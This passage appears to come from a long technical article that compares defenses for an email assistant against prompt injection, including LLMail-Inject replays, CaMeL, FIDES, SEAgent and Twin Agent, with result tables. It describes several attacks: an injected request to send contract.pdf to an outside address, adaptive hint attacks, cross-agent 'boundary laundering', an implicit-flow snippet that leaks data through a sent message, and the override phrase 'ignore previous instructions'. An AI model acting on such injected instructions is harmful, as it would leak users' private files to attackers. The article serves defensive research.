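- *Level 2.* It read ten emails, with the attacker's in the middle.
- *Level 3.* It searched the mailbox, so the attacker's email also had to appear in the search results.
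- *Level 4.* It searched as in level 3, and the attacker had to steal a profit forecast from another email.

Participants attacked two models, Phi-3-medium and GPT-4o-mini, protected by one of five defenses. One defense marked the emails as untrusted text. Three tried to detect attacks, using a text classifier, a language model as judge, or measurements of the assistant's internal activity. The fifth combined the other four. Participants knew how the defenses worked, and after each attempt they learned which stages it had passed. After the first phase, the organizers strengthened the defenses and ran the contest again.

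In the first phase, fewer than 1% of submissions passed every stage. Many of the successful attacks read like ordinary office mail. In one, a supposed colleague asked whether the recipient had remembered to send a confirmation, complained about the boss, and offered pizza and beer as thanks.

### 649 attacks against two agents

Cheng and Tsao, of Trend Micro's AI lab, replayed first-phase attacks against OpenClaw running on gpt-5-mini. They started with 41,173 submissions that they describe as successes and removed duplicates, leaving 22,899. Against a single agent with no added defense, 649 of these (2.83%) succeeded.

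They then ran the 649 against three other setups. In the two-agent setups, the reader could only store a summary, and the actor could fetch that summary and send mail. "Structured output" means the summary had to be a JSON record with fields for sender, subject, body summary and action items.

| Setup | Successful attacks out of 649 | Attack success rate |
|---|---|---|
| One agent | 649 | 100% |
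| One agent, structured output | 92 | 14.18% |
| Two agents | 2 | 0.31% |
| Two agents, structured output | 0 | 0% |

Structured output alone was weakest on level 4, where 49 of the 173 data thefts still succeeded. Neither two-agent setup let any of those through.

The 2.83% figure is a poor measure of how well gpt-5-mini resists injection in general. Abdelnabi and colleagues replayed contest attacks on the same model in their own assistant, and 47% succeeded. The two studies used different software and probably different selections of attacks. Cheng and Tsao's starting set of "successes" also seems to include many attacks that failed in the contest. Its size matches the roughly 41,200 first-phase submissions that got the assistant to call the sending tool at all. The contest's defenses detected about 34,000 of those, and many of the rest sent the wrong message.

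### What the zero supports

The table shows 100% for the single agent because Cheng and Tsao picked the 649 attacks that had succeeded against it. A model doesn't respond the same way every time, so some of those attacks may have succeeded by luck. A second run against the same agent might have produced fewer than 649 successes, but Cheng and Tsao don't report one.

If luck were the only factor, each of the 22,899 attacks would have the same 2.83% chance of success, and rerunning the 649 that succeeded would produce about 18 successes. But 92 of them also worked against the single agent with structured output. Unless structured output makes an agent easier to attack, a rerun without it would probably have produced between 92 and 649 successes. Two successes would then be roughly a 46- to 325-fold reduction. Even a 46-fold reduction is large, though Cheng and Tsao's own figure, 323, is near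 the top of the range.

The drop from two successful attacks to zero is much less certain. If the two designs were equally safe, two successful attacks would both hit the same design half the time. The experiment therefore doesn't show that structured output adds any protection once the agents are separate.

Zero successes in 649 attempts is also compatible with a true success rate of up to about 0.46% (the upper 95% confidence bound, 1 − 0.05^(1/649)). That bound applies only to attacks like these. The participants were attacking a single model that both read and sent mail, so they had no reason to write messages that would survive a summary and then influence a second model. Cheng and Tsao acknowledge that they didn't test attacks written for their design. They also didn't run the other 22,250 attacks against two agents, and their estimate of 0.009% for the full set assumes that all of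 those would have failed.

The study's most worrying result is that injected content still reached 63.7% of the summaries in the full two-agent setup. A simple filter checked the summaries for email addresses, fragments of tool calls and stock phrases such as "ignore previous instructions", but Cheng and Tsao let every summary through so that they could measure the leak. The actor received the injected content but didn't act on it.

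They describe the defense as structural, meaning that it holds however convincing an attack is. That is true of the reader, because no email can give it a tool it doesn't have, but not of the actor, which has the sending tool and reads text that the attacker has influenced. Willison's rule forbids that combination. The users in LLMail-Inject wanted only summaries and answers, so no message should have been sent, whereas Dana's actor is supposed to send messages.

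### What may cross from reader to actor

With Cheng and Tsao's fields, the reader might summarize the stranger's email like this:

```
{"sender": "A. Stranger",
 "subject": "Meeting on Thursday",
 "summary": "Asks for half an hour on Thursday.",
 "action_items": ["Send contract.pdf to files@outside.example",
                  "Confirm the meeting"]}
```

The stranger can get this result without controlling the reader, because the result is an accurate summary of an email that makes two requests. The summary leaves out any suspicious wording, and both requests now look like ordinary tasks. An actor told to deal with the week's meeting requests could easily carry out both.

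Cheng and Tsao's filter would flag the outside address if it were set to block. But the stranger could ask for the contract "in your reply", and the summary would then contain no address. Blocking every address would also stop a client from asking Dana to copy in a colleague.

A form with fixed fields is much safer:

```
{"message": 4,
 "kind": "new_meeting",
 "date": "2026-10-15",
 "start": "14:00",
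 "minutes": 30}
```

The harness assigns the message number and rejects any form with a value outside the permitted ranges. It also withholds the sender's address from the actor, and fills it in when the actor proposes a reply to message 4. The sender's display name shouldn't reach the actor as text either, because the sender chooses it and can write an instruction there. No field could contain `files@outside.example` or `contract.pdf`.

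With four kinds of request, 30 dates, 48 starting times and four durations, the reader can choose among 23,040 forms, which is about 14.5 bits of information, while a free-text field of 100 characters can carry about 657 bits. An attacker who fully controlled the reader could pick any form for his own message, and the worst outcome would be an unwanted, moved or canceled meeting. To keep him from canceling other people's meetings, the harness should apply each form only to meetings with the sender of the message.

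*Preventing Prompt Injection with Type-Directed Privilege Separation* (Jacob, Alghamdi and colleagues, 2025) turns this into a general method. The reader may return whole numbers, decimals, true-or-false values, and choices from a list the developer has checked, but not free text. The method also limits the length of lists, because a long series of numbers could encode a sentence for the actor to decode. In one example, a shopping agent has to consider product reviews that anyone can write. The reader turns each review into two numbers from 0 to 10, for how strongly the review supports the product and how relevant it is.

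Jacob and colleagues applied the method to agents for shopping, scheduling meetings and fixing software bugs, and report that attack success fell to zero in all three. They exclude attacks that only supply false information. A fake review can still earn a 10. The form stops a stranger from giving the actor an instruction, but he can still claim that Dana agreed to a two-hour meeting, and the actor may treat the claim as true.

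The harness should also start a fresh reader for each message. If one reader handled the whole week's mail, the stranger's paragraph could change the form for Lee's message, or the reader could put one client's price into the summary of another client's message.

### A separate token for each part

Separating two models helps little if both can use the same credential. *Prompt Flow Integrity* gives them different access tokens. The actor's token works with every tool, while the reader's permits nothing by default. If an attacker took over the reader and found a way to call the mail API, the API would reject the call.

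A broker could enforce the same division without giving either part a token. It would identify which part was calling and attach Dana's token only to the actor's requests. The mail providers' broad scopes matter less for the reader because it doesn't fetch mail; the harness gives it the text of one message.

*Prompt Flow Integrity to Prevent Privilege Escalation in LLM Agents* replaces untrusted text with identifiers such as `#DATA0`, which work like Willison's variables. It treats calendar events the same way, so an actor would see the description of a stranger's invitation only as an identifier. Two checks cover what the actor does with the identifiers:

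- *Data flow.* If an argument in the actor's call contains an identifier, and the reader's token wouldn't permit that call, the software alerts the user. The alert shows the hidden text, where it came from and where it is going. The same check applies to the final answer.
- *Control flow.* The actor may ask to read a piece of untrusted text as instructions. It receives the text only if the user approves.

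The system was tested on AgentDojo, with some tasks changed to depend on untrusted material. The attacks included injected instructions, as well as false information and phishing links that contained no instructions.

| Model | Tasks completed, ordinary agent → separated | Tasks attacked successfully, ordinary agent → separated |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 81.4% → 61.9% | 81.4% → 0% |
| GPT-4o mini | 63.9% → 48.5% | 63.9% → 0% |
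| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 80.4% → 64.9% | 39.2% → 0% |
| Gemini 1.5 Pro | 64.9% → 47.4% | 47.4% → 0% |

The zeros depend on counting an alert as a successful defense because the user might refuse the action. No real users took part in the test. Most testers in Anthropic's experiment approved a dangerous command, so some of Dana's alerts would probably fail too.

The system raised 1.49 alerts per task with GPT-4o, compared with 4.11 for an agent that asked about every call. The paper claims no false positives, but it counts an alert as correct if untrusted data reached a privileged call. An alert about a harmless reply to Sam would count as correct if his address came from his message.

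Dana could reduce the alerts by marking some senders as always trusted, but the actor would then read their messages in full. The policy in the tests trusted everyone at the user's own company, so the actor would read the stranger's paragraph if a colleague forwarded the email. The risk is worse if the assistant has its own mailbox, as suggested earlier, because every request Dana forwards comes from her own trusted address.

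The same policy let the reader open public web pages. If a query included both the stranger's email and a confidential one from Lee, instructions in the stranger's email could make the reader put Lee's text into a web address, which is how ShadowLeak worked. Dana's reader should keep the default token, which permits nothing.

The same tests show why the return channel matters. IsolateGPT, an earlier design, gives each application its own agent but lets those agents return ordinary text to a central planner. With GPT-4o, attacks still succeeded on 72.2% of tasks, not much below the 81.4% for an agent with no separation. The tests used the competing project's reimplementation of IsolateGPT, and the count includes false information, which IsolateGPT wasn't built to stop. Even with those caveats, the rate is far higher than Cheng and Tsao's two successful attacks in 649.

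### Requests the actor can't handle without reading

*Prompt Flow Integrity* also increased the average time per AgentDojo task from 5.45 to 8.91 seconds and the cost by 88%. More seriously, across the four models, 108 tasks that succeeded with the ordinary agent failed with the separated one. In 55% of these, the actor used an identifier incorrectly, and in another 21% it sent the reader a badly framed question. The models were released in 2024, and newer ones may make fewer of these mistakes.

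Other failures would remain even with a perfect model, because the actor needs to know what the message says. The requests Dana might make differ a great deal in this respect:

| Dana's request | What the actor has to learn from the mail | Does it work? |
|---|---|---|
| Summarize today's mail | Nothing | Yes, the harness shows her the reader's text |
| Forward Lee's last message to Ana | Nothing | Yes, the actor refers to the message by its variable |
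| Book the half hour Lee wants | A date, a time and a length | Yes, with a form |
| Invite the colleague Lee mentions | An address | Only with a variable for an address that the sender chose |
| Answer Lee's question about his renewal | The question | Not without free text |
| Do whatever Lee asks | Everything | No |

Answering a question like Lee's is a common task, but it is hard to do with this separation because the reader has the question and only the actor can look up the answer. A developer might give the reader Dana's files, let it write the reply, and have the harness send the text without showing it to the actor. But then the stranger could ask what the contract says, and the harness would mail him the reader's answer. Even without tools, a reader can leak private data if it is given that data and its output is sent to the attacker.

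Standard separation fails completely on some other kinds of work. *Twin Agent* (Hu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026) tested agents that repair software by following bug reports, which anyone can submit. An ordinary agent on GPT-5.2 repaired 61.2% of the bugs. When the actor could neither read the report nor receive anything from the reader, it repaired none. Mail suits separation better because a form can hold the details of most meeting requests.

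### Attacks written for separated agents

Twin Agent is a compromise that lets a little free text reach the actor. The reader can see what the actor has done so far, so instead of summarizing the whole report, it can send a hint of up to 100 characters at each step with whatever the actor still needs. Another model checks each hint for injection and blocks suspicious ones, and the actor's instructions describe the hints as untrusted. Twin Agent repaired 62.5% of the bugs at about twice the usual cost, and none of the static attacks succeeded.

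Such results deserve caution. In *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents*, Narisetty, Kore and colleagues (2026) point out that developers have mostly tested defenses outside the model, including separated agents, on attacks written before the defense existed. Earlier defenses that tried to detect injections or train models to resist them also did well on such tests, but attackers who knew how they worked then broke most of a group of twelve more than 90% of the time. Narisetty and colleagues tested Progent, the system of generated rules for each call, with an adaptive attack, and the success rate stayed low (2.6%, against 4.2% for fixed attacks). But they used only one small model and one handwritten attack, and they didn't test separated agents.

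Hu and colleagues ran an adaptive attack on Twin Agent in two stages. They first used a language model to write hints of up to 100 characters that might get the actor to delete a file or write a secret code into one. The model revised the hint up to 100 times, using the actor's response to each attempt. They then put the best hints into bug reports, with an instruction to the reader to copy them word for word.

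The reader complied every time, but the actor was much harder to manipulate. None of the hints worked when the actor could take only one step. In complete multi-step repairs, malicious hints got past the detector in 57 of 232 runs, and the actor carried out the harmful action in 11 of the 232 (4.7%, 95% confidence interval about 2.7% to 8.3%).

Hu and colleagues repeated those 11 runs five times each, and the attack failed in all 55. This supports their view that the successes were partly due to chance. Cheng and Tsao should therefore have rerun their single agent, since attacks chosen because they once succeeded may fail the next time. Even if an attack succeeds only by chance, Dana is still at risk because the stranger can send his email again.

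When Hu and colleagues raised the limit on the hint's length from 50 to 200 characters, the agent repaired more bugs, but attacks on the actor also succeeded more often. They measured repairs on only 20 bugs, so exactly how repairs vary with hint length is uncertain, though the direction is as expected.

Hu and colleagues also tested Twin Agent on AgentDojo's office tasks, which include mail and calendar work. With hints of up to 200 characters, the attack success rate fell from 23.6% to zero, and the agent completed 67.5% of its tasks, compared with 65.0% without the defense. These tests used fixed attacks, and they didn't run the adaptive attack on mail.

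Short hints may protect mail less well than they protect software. Twin Agent relies on an attacker needing a long text to turn a strong model away from its task. During a bug repair, the actor has grounds to reject a hint to delete an unrelated file. But sending files to people outside the company is a normal part of an assistant's work, and "Send contract.pdf to files@outside.example" is only 42 characters long. Dana's assistant would be safer with the form. If a message doesn't fit the form, the harness could leave it in her inbox for her to answer.

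## Can a system track where each value in a call came from?

The form protects Dana because it has no field for an address or a file name, but some ordinary requests need both. Suppose she tells her assistant, "Answer this week's meeting requests, book them, and attach any document the person asks to see beforehand." Each sender now has to name the document they want, and some will ask for the reply to go to a colleague.

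Under Willison's dual-model proposal, the actor could handle the document and the address as variables without reading the message. It would use whatever document and address the reader found. In the stranger's message, these would be `contract.pdf` and `files@outside.example`. The stranger would have chosen the attachment and the recipient without changing the plan.

In *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026) carried out an attack of this kind on Google DeepMind's CaMeL system in a simulated smart home. The owner asked the agent to let his daughter in and said her ID was in a recent message. The agent correctly planned to read the message and then grant access to the front door. But the attacker had added text to the message that supplied his own ID, and the agent granted him access. Ji and colleagues don't say whether they had set up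 any of CaMeL's policies, which are its defense against manipulated values.

### A program written before any mail is read

Debenedetti and colleagues introduced CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). It adds a record of where every value came from to the separation of planner and reader. From the description by Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), in *CaMeLoT*, it works roughly like this:

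1. The planner receives the user's request and the tool descriptions, but no mail. It writes a program in a restricted form of Python that contains every call the agent might make.
2. An interpreter, which is ordinary software, runs the program and calls the tools.
3. When the program needs information from a text, the interpreter gives the text to a reader without tools, which returns values in a fixed structure.
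4. The interpreter labels each value with its sources and with the people who may read it. A value computed from other values takes its labels from them.
5. Before each call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short function that receives the tool's name, the arguments and their labels. The policy allows or refuses the call and gives a reason.

CaMeL calls these labels "capabilities", but they describe a value, whereas Hardy's capabilities confer a right.

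### Dana's program and its labels

For Dana's longer request, the planner might write:

```
for m in search_mail("meeting request", since="2026-10-05"):
    r    = ask_reader("Extract the request", m, MeetingRequest)
    slot = find_free_time(r.day, r.minutes)
    file = find_attachment(r.document)
    create_event(start=slot, minutes=r.minutes)
    send_message(to=r.reply_to,
                 text="Dana can meet at " + slot,
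                 attachments=[file])
```

The developer could treat an email's sender and recipients as its permitted readers. When a value depends on two others, only people who may read both may read the result. Suppose Dana's lawyer sent her the contract. When the loop reaches the stranger's message, the labels are:

| Value | Content | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|---|
| `r.reply_to` | `files@outside.example` | The stranger's message | Dana, the stranger |
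| `r.document` | `contract.pdf` | The stranger's message | Dana, the stranger |
| `slot` | Thursday, 2 pm | Dana's calendar, the stranger's message | Anyone |
| `file` | The contract | The lawyer's message, the stranger's message | Dana |

The lawyer may read the contract, but only Dana may read `file`, because the file name came from the stranger's message, which the lawyer may not read. Dana's calendar is private, so under the usual rule the assistant couldn't tell anyone when she was free. The developer has to make an exception for `slot`.

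A simple policy for sending mail checks the recipient against these labels:

```
def check_send(to, text, attachments):
    for value in [text] + attachments:
        if to not in readers(value):
            return deny("The recipient may not read this.")
    return allow()
```

The interpreter allows `create_event`, which has no guests. It refuses `send_message` because `files@outside.example` isn't permitted to read the contract. The result is the same whether the reader followed the stranger's instructions or summarized them accurately.

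For this week's other mail, the same policy works better than a fixed list of contacts. If Lee asks for an agenda that Dana has already sent him, he receives it because he is a permitted reader. Sam gets his appointment although he isn't a contact, because anyone may read the proposed time. If the program copied Ana's price from her message into the answer to Lee, a mistake the recipient rules couldn't catch, the policy would refuse the call because only Dana and Ana may read that message.

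Under this policy, the stranger could still direct a message to any address he liked, as long as it had no attachment. To prevent this, the developer could require every address to come from Dana, her contacts or the sender field of the message being answered. But then the assistant couldn't write to a colleague whom Lee mentions in his text.

### CaMeL on AgentDojo

Most tests of CaMeL, like those of Progent, use the benchmark that *AgentDojo* (2024) introduced. Its workspace tasks involve email, a calendar and a cloud drive. Each attack case pairs a user's request with an attacker's goal, such as obtaining a two-factor sign-in code. As *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) explains, ordinary code then checks the simulated accounts to see whether the attack succeeded, so no language model has to judge the result.

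*SecureClaw* (2026) reports a full run of CaMeL's released code, adapted to the paper's test setup. None of the 629 attacks succeeded, but with no attack present, CaMeL completed only 29 of the 97 tasks (29.9%). The paper's own defense completed 59.

CaMeL's completion rate depends partly on whether its planner is told the format of each tool's output in advance. An ordinary agent can read a tool's output before deciding what to do with it, but CaMeL's planner has to write code for data it hasn't seen. In *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) found that they had to add a description of every tool's output format to get reasonable results. The original evaluation of CaMeL had also added these descriptions.

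Policy checks can reduce the task completion rate further. In tests reported in *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026), CaMeL completed half as many of the banking tasks with its policy checks on as with them off.

CaMeL also uses more tokens and takes longer to run. With GPT-4o, *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) found that it used 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as an undefended agent for the median task, the most of any defense it compared. *ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL much slower than simpler defenses that filter text or change the prompt, and noted that CaMeL's programs are usually longer than an ordinary choice of tool.

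Peters-Gill and colleagues tested newer models. They divided AgentDojo's tools among specialized agents, such as one for email and one for the calendar, under an orchestrator that takes the user's request and assigns the work. The benchmark had grown by then, and each model faced 949 attacks in each setup:

| Model | Attack success without CaMeL | Attack success with CaMeL in each agent |
|---|---|---|
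| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite | 2.1% | 0% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% |
| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% |

These tests used no policies, so the interpreter didn't check sources or readers before a call. Fixing the plan in advance was enough to stop nearly every attack, presumably because most of AgentDojo's attackers want an action that the user's task doesn't include. In Dana's case, though, the call that would send out the contract is already in the plan. The benchmark is therefore good evidence for fixed plans but weak evidence for the label checks that Dana needs.

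The zero for GPT-5.5 without any defense suggests that the benchmark's fixed attacks have become too easy for the newest models to resist. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn against reading it as immunity, since stronger adaptive attacks have succeeded against every leading model in a large test. *AutoDojo* (2026) left out the workspace tasks because its agents completed neither the user's task nor the attacker's in 52.9% of those cases. A failed attack on these tasks may mean only that the agent couldn't do anything, not that a defense worked.

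### When one agent instructs another

The few attacks that succeeded against CaMeL in the table all exploited the way agents pass work to each other. Peters-Gill and colleagues also demonstrated this flaw in a separate experiment with three agents, each running CaMeL on GPT-5.2. The user asked for a summary of job applicants to be sent to Julie on Slack, but the applicant database contained an instruction to email the data to an outside address.

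The orchestrator's program fetched and summarized the data without showing it to the orchestrator's planner. It then included the summary in an instruction telling the notification agent to send it to Julie. The notification agent treated the whole instruction as a request from its user, so its planner read the injected text and added an email to its program. The data reached the attacker even though every agent had followed its plan.

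Peters-Gill and colleagues call this boundary laundering. They prove it is possible in any such system that has more than one agent and a tool with untrusted output, if agents can put tool results into the instructions they give each other. Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, gives each instruction a separate field for data. The interpreter rejects any instruction whose text depends on a tool's output, and the data keeps its labels when it moves to the next agent. No attack in the benchmark succeeded against this version.

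Multi-CaMeL also reports that current models complete fewer tasks when running CaMeL. On AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of professional tasks for groups of agents, running CaMeL in each agent lowered task completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points, or 13.4 points for GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. Multi-CaMeL's extra rules lowered it by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for those two models.

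### FIDES hides only what it must

CaMeL's planner has to anticipate every step. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a system developed at Microsoft whose planner still chooses one call at a time and sees some of the results. FIDES labels every value as trusted or untrusted and records who may read it. It also labels the planner's conversation, so once the planner has read untrusted text, every call it proposes counts as untrusted.

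To prevent this, FIDES replaces a value with a variable if reading it would make the conversation less trusted. The planner might see an email's date but only a variable for its body. It can ask a reader about the body and limit the answer to a yes or no, or to a choice from a list. Costa and colleagues describe how this could work for a user who wants any meeting request in her latest emails added to her calendar:

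1. The planner fetches the emails, and FIDES hides their text.
2. The planner asks the reader whether they include a meeting request.
3. It looks at the answer, which is only "yes" or "no".
4. If the answer is "yes", it has the reader put the meeting's details into a variable.
5. It creates the event from that variable without seeing the details.

The stranger can influence the planner only through the one-bit answer in step 3, which a policy can accept because it is too short to contain an instruction. But he can still influence the details in step 4, so the developer has to decide which of those details may come from a message.

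FIDES has two basic policies. One allows a consequential call only if the choice of call and its arguments are trusted, and the other allows data to go only to permitted readers. A developer can relax the first policy for particular arguments. For example, the developer could let untrusted mail influence a message's text but not its recipient.

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. The attack counts cover all four groups of tasks, and the completion rates are for the workspace tasks without an attack:

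| Setup | Successful attacks | Workspace tasks completed |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 152 | 75.0% |
| Ordinary agent with policies | 0 | 37.0% |
| FIDES without policies | 21 | 63.5% |
| FIDES with policies | 0 | 59.0% |

The policies stop the attacks in either design, and hiding text lets the agent complete more tasks under them. Across the four groups, FIDES completed about 8 percentage points more tasks than an ordinary agent with the same policies. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, the gap was about 16 points. With GPT-4o, FIDES did worse on travel tasks, where the policies allowed most calls and the model often misused the variables.

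Costa and colleagues removed some attacks from the counts after inspecting them by hand, including a group that had altered the agent's text without changing its calls or leaking private data. Excluding that group is reasonable for a test of information flow, but a false sentence in an answer to a client could still harm Dana.

The version they tested also left out the restricted answers in step 3, because most AgentDojo tasks didn't need them. By their count, only 5% of the workspace tasks (two of 40) require the agent to choose its actions based on what it reads, compared with 43.8% of the banking tasks. Dana's request also requires this, so the 59.0% may overestimate how well FIDES would handle her mail.

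### Labels on tools

SEAgent, the access control framework that Ji and colleagues published in January 2026, labels tools, agents and databases instead of values. A tool's labels describe whether it reads, writes or executes, how sensitive the operation is, and whether its output is trustworthy or private. SEAgent draws a graph of how information moves between tools and agents during a task, and compares it with forbidden patterns. One rule in simplified form is:

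```
deny   tool A → ... → tool B
if     A returns unfiltered material from outside
and    B writes or executes something of moderate or high sensitivity
```

This is mandatory access control, in which fixed rules apply regardless of what the agent decides. It doesn't require a new kind of planner or a record for every value.

The rule is too coarse for Dana. Reading mail returns unfiltered material from outside, and sending mail is a sensitive operation, so the rule would block both the reply to Lee and the theft of the contract. If the developer labeled incoming mail as trustworthy, the rule would block neither. SEAgent can also compare arguments with a pattern, such as an approved email domain, but that brings back the fixed list of recipients. If no rule matches a call, SEAgent allows it.

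On AgentDojo, SEAgent reduced attack success from 39.14% to zero overall, and from 26.46% to zero on the workspace tasks. Ji and colleagues measured its usefulness on different benchmarks, so we don't know how many of AgentDojo's mail tasks it would have blocked. On API-Bank, a set of ordinary tool-use tasks, the agent made correct calls about as often with SEAgent as without it, and the rules wrongly stopped only two tasks. In both, the agent had looked something up on Wikipedia before trying to record health data or register an appointment. Ji and colleagues switched the rules off in the tests with several agents.

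The three systems therefore offer different protection even though all of them report zero successful attacks on AgentDojo:

| | CaMeL | FIDES | SEAgent |
|---|---|---|---|
| What has labels | Each value | Each value and the planner's conversation | Tools, agents and databases |
| When the planner chooses calls | Before any mail is read | Step by step, with untrusted text hidden | Step by step, with the text visible |
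| What a stranger's text can still affect | Which planned branch runs, and values the policy allows | Restricted answers, and values the policy allows | Any call or value that no rule forbids |
| What its developers have proved | No theorem that its tracking is sound | Private data can't flow directly to people who may not read it | Its memory component adds no new route for attacks |

### Leaks through what the assistant does

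FIDES's guarantee covers data that the assistant sends, but people can also learn from its actions. If the stranger asks for a different half hour every day and notes which ones the assistant accepts, he will gradually learn when Dana is busy, even though no message contains her calendar. Costa and colleagues accept such leaks because the stricter alternative would essentially forbid the assistant from doing anything an outsider could observe after it had read anything private, so Dana's assistant could never answer a meeting request.

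CaMeL tries to track some of these indirect leaks, but Garby and colleagues found a gap. A simplified version of their example is:

```
tmp  = True
rich = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_message("m@outside.example", "Hello")
```

If the balance is high, the third line sets `tmp` to false and CaMeL labels `tmp` private. The fourth line doesn't run, so `rich` stays true and keeps its public label. The last line sends a message, which tells the recipient that the balance is high. If the balance is low, no message arrives. CaMeL labels a variable only when a line that changes it runs, so it doesn't account for what the skipped line reveals about the balance. Computer scientists have known about this pattern since the 1970s.

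A stranger couldn't insert these lines into Dana's program, because the planner writes the program before reading his message. The planner could still write something similar by accident. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL's tracking doesn't cover its retry loop. Whether a policy blocks a run can reveal one bit of private data, and someone able to trigger repeated runs could extract a whole secret.

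Their own system, LLMbda, is a small programming language for agents that closes these gaps, with computer-checked proofs. On AgentDojo's banking tasks, an agent written in it completed about as many tasks as CaMeL did without policies, and attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. In both of those runs, the planner's program had explicitly marked untrusted data as trusted, which the language permits because real tasks sometimes need this exception. The proofs establish limits on what an exception can affect, but not whether making it was wise.

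### When the message should decide

Dana often wants a message to determine what the assistant does. For example, the assistant should delete the meeting if Lee cancels and move it if he suggests another time. CaMeL can handle this if the planner writes a branch for each case in advance. The stranger can then choose among the branches, but he can't add one. The developer has to make sure that every branch is safe for any sender.

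This doesn't work for requests such as "do whatever Lee asks", because the planner can't list every action beforehand. In many of AgentDojo's banking tasks, the user similarly asks the agent to follow the instructions in a file, and FIDES blocks this because the file is untrusted. Costa and colleagues count these failures as intended. If Dana marked Lee's messages as trusted, anyone who took over his account could give her assistant orders.

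Labels also don't show whether a statement is true. In the smart home, a policy that refused any ID taken from a message would have kept out both the attacker and the daughter, because both IDs were in the same message. An email could also make the reader return an empty summary, and the label would correctly name the email as the source. The harness could show Dana the source beside each statement, but she would still have to check whether the statements were true.

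### Who writes the policies

Someone has to supply the labels and rules. This is easier for email than for most data because each message lists its sender and recipients, and mail servers can often verify the sender's domain. But Costa and colleagues point out that people may have shared a message more widely than its address lines show, in which case the policy would refuse to send a document to someone who already had it.

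According to *Agent-Sentry* (2026), developers write CaMeL's policies separately for each agent, based on a full description of its tools and data. Users can't easily take over this work. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026), which adapts CaMeL to agents that operate a computer's screen, notes that most users can't judge what risks a policy allows. The paper omits such policies and instead restricts how the program may use the reader. An assistant that only handles meeting requests is an easier case, because Dana's program makes only two kinds of call that change anything.

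Nikolaou and colleagues reduce the work wasted when a policy stops a program halfway. Their extension, CaMeLoT, checks the whole program before it calls any tool. A rule might require that a message's recipient never come from an untrusted source. Dana's program would fail this check because `r.reply_to` comes from the reader. CaMeLoT would show the planner a sequence of steps that breaks the rule, and the planner could repair the program by using the message's sender field instead. CaMeLoT can also require that something eventually happens, such as every meeting request getting an answer. The check treats a loop as if it could run any number of times, so it may reject some safe programs.

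Even good policies will refuse calls that Dana wants. If Sam asks for a brochure that Dana has sent only to Lee, the policy will refuse the call because Sam isn't a permitted reader. The harness could ask Dana to approve it, but frequent questions would lead to the approval fatigue seen with coding agents. Labels at least let the harness give her more to go on than a question about whether to send a message. It could tell her that the address and the file name both came from a stranger's email, and that she received the file from her lawyer.

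SEAgent's rules can also require the user's approval, and the prompt shows the path the information took. The user can choose to always allow that pattern. If Dana chose this for Lee, SEAgent might never ask her about the contract, because the path from reading mail to sending mail is the same for Lee as for the stranger.
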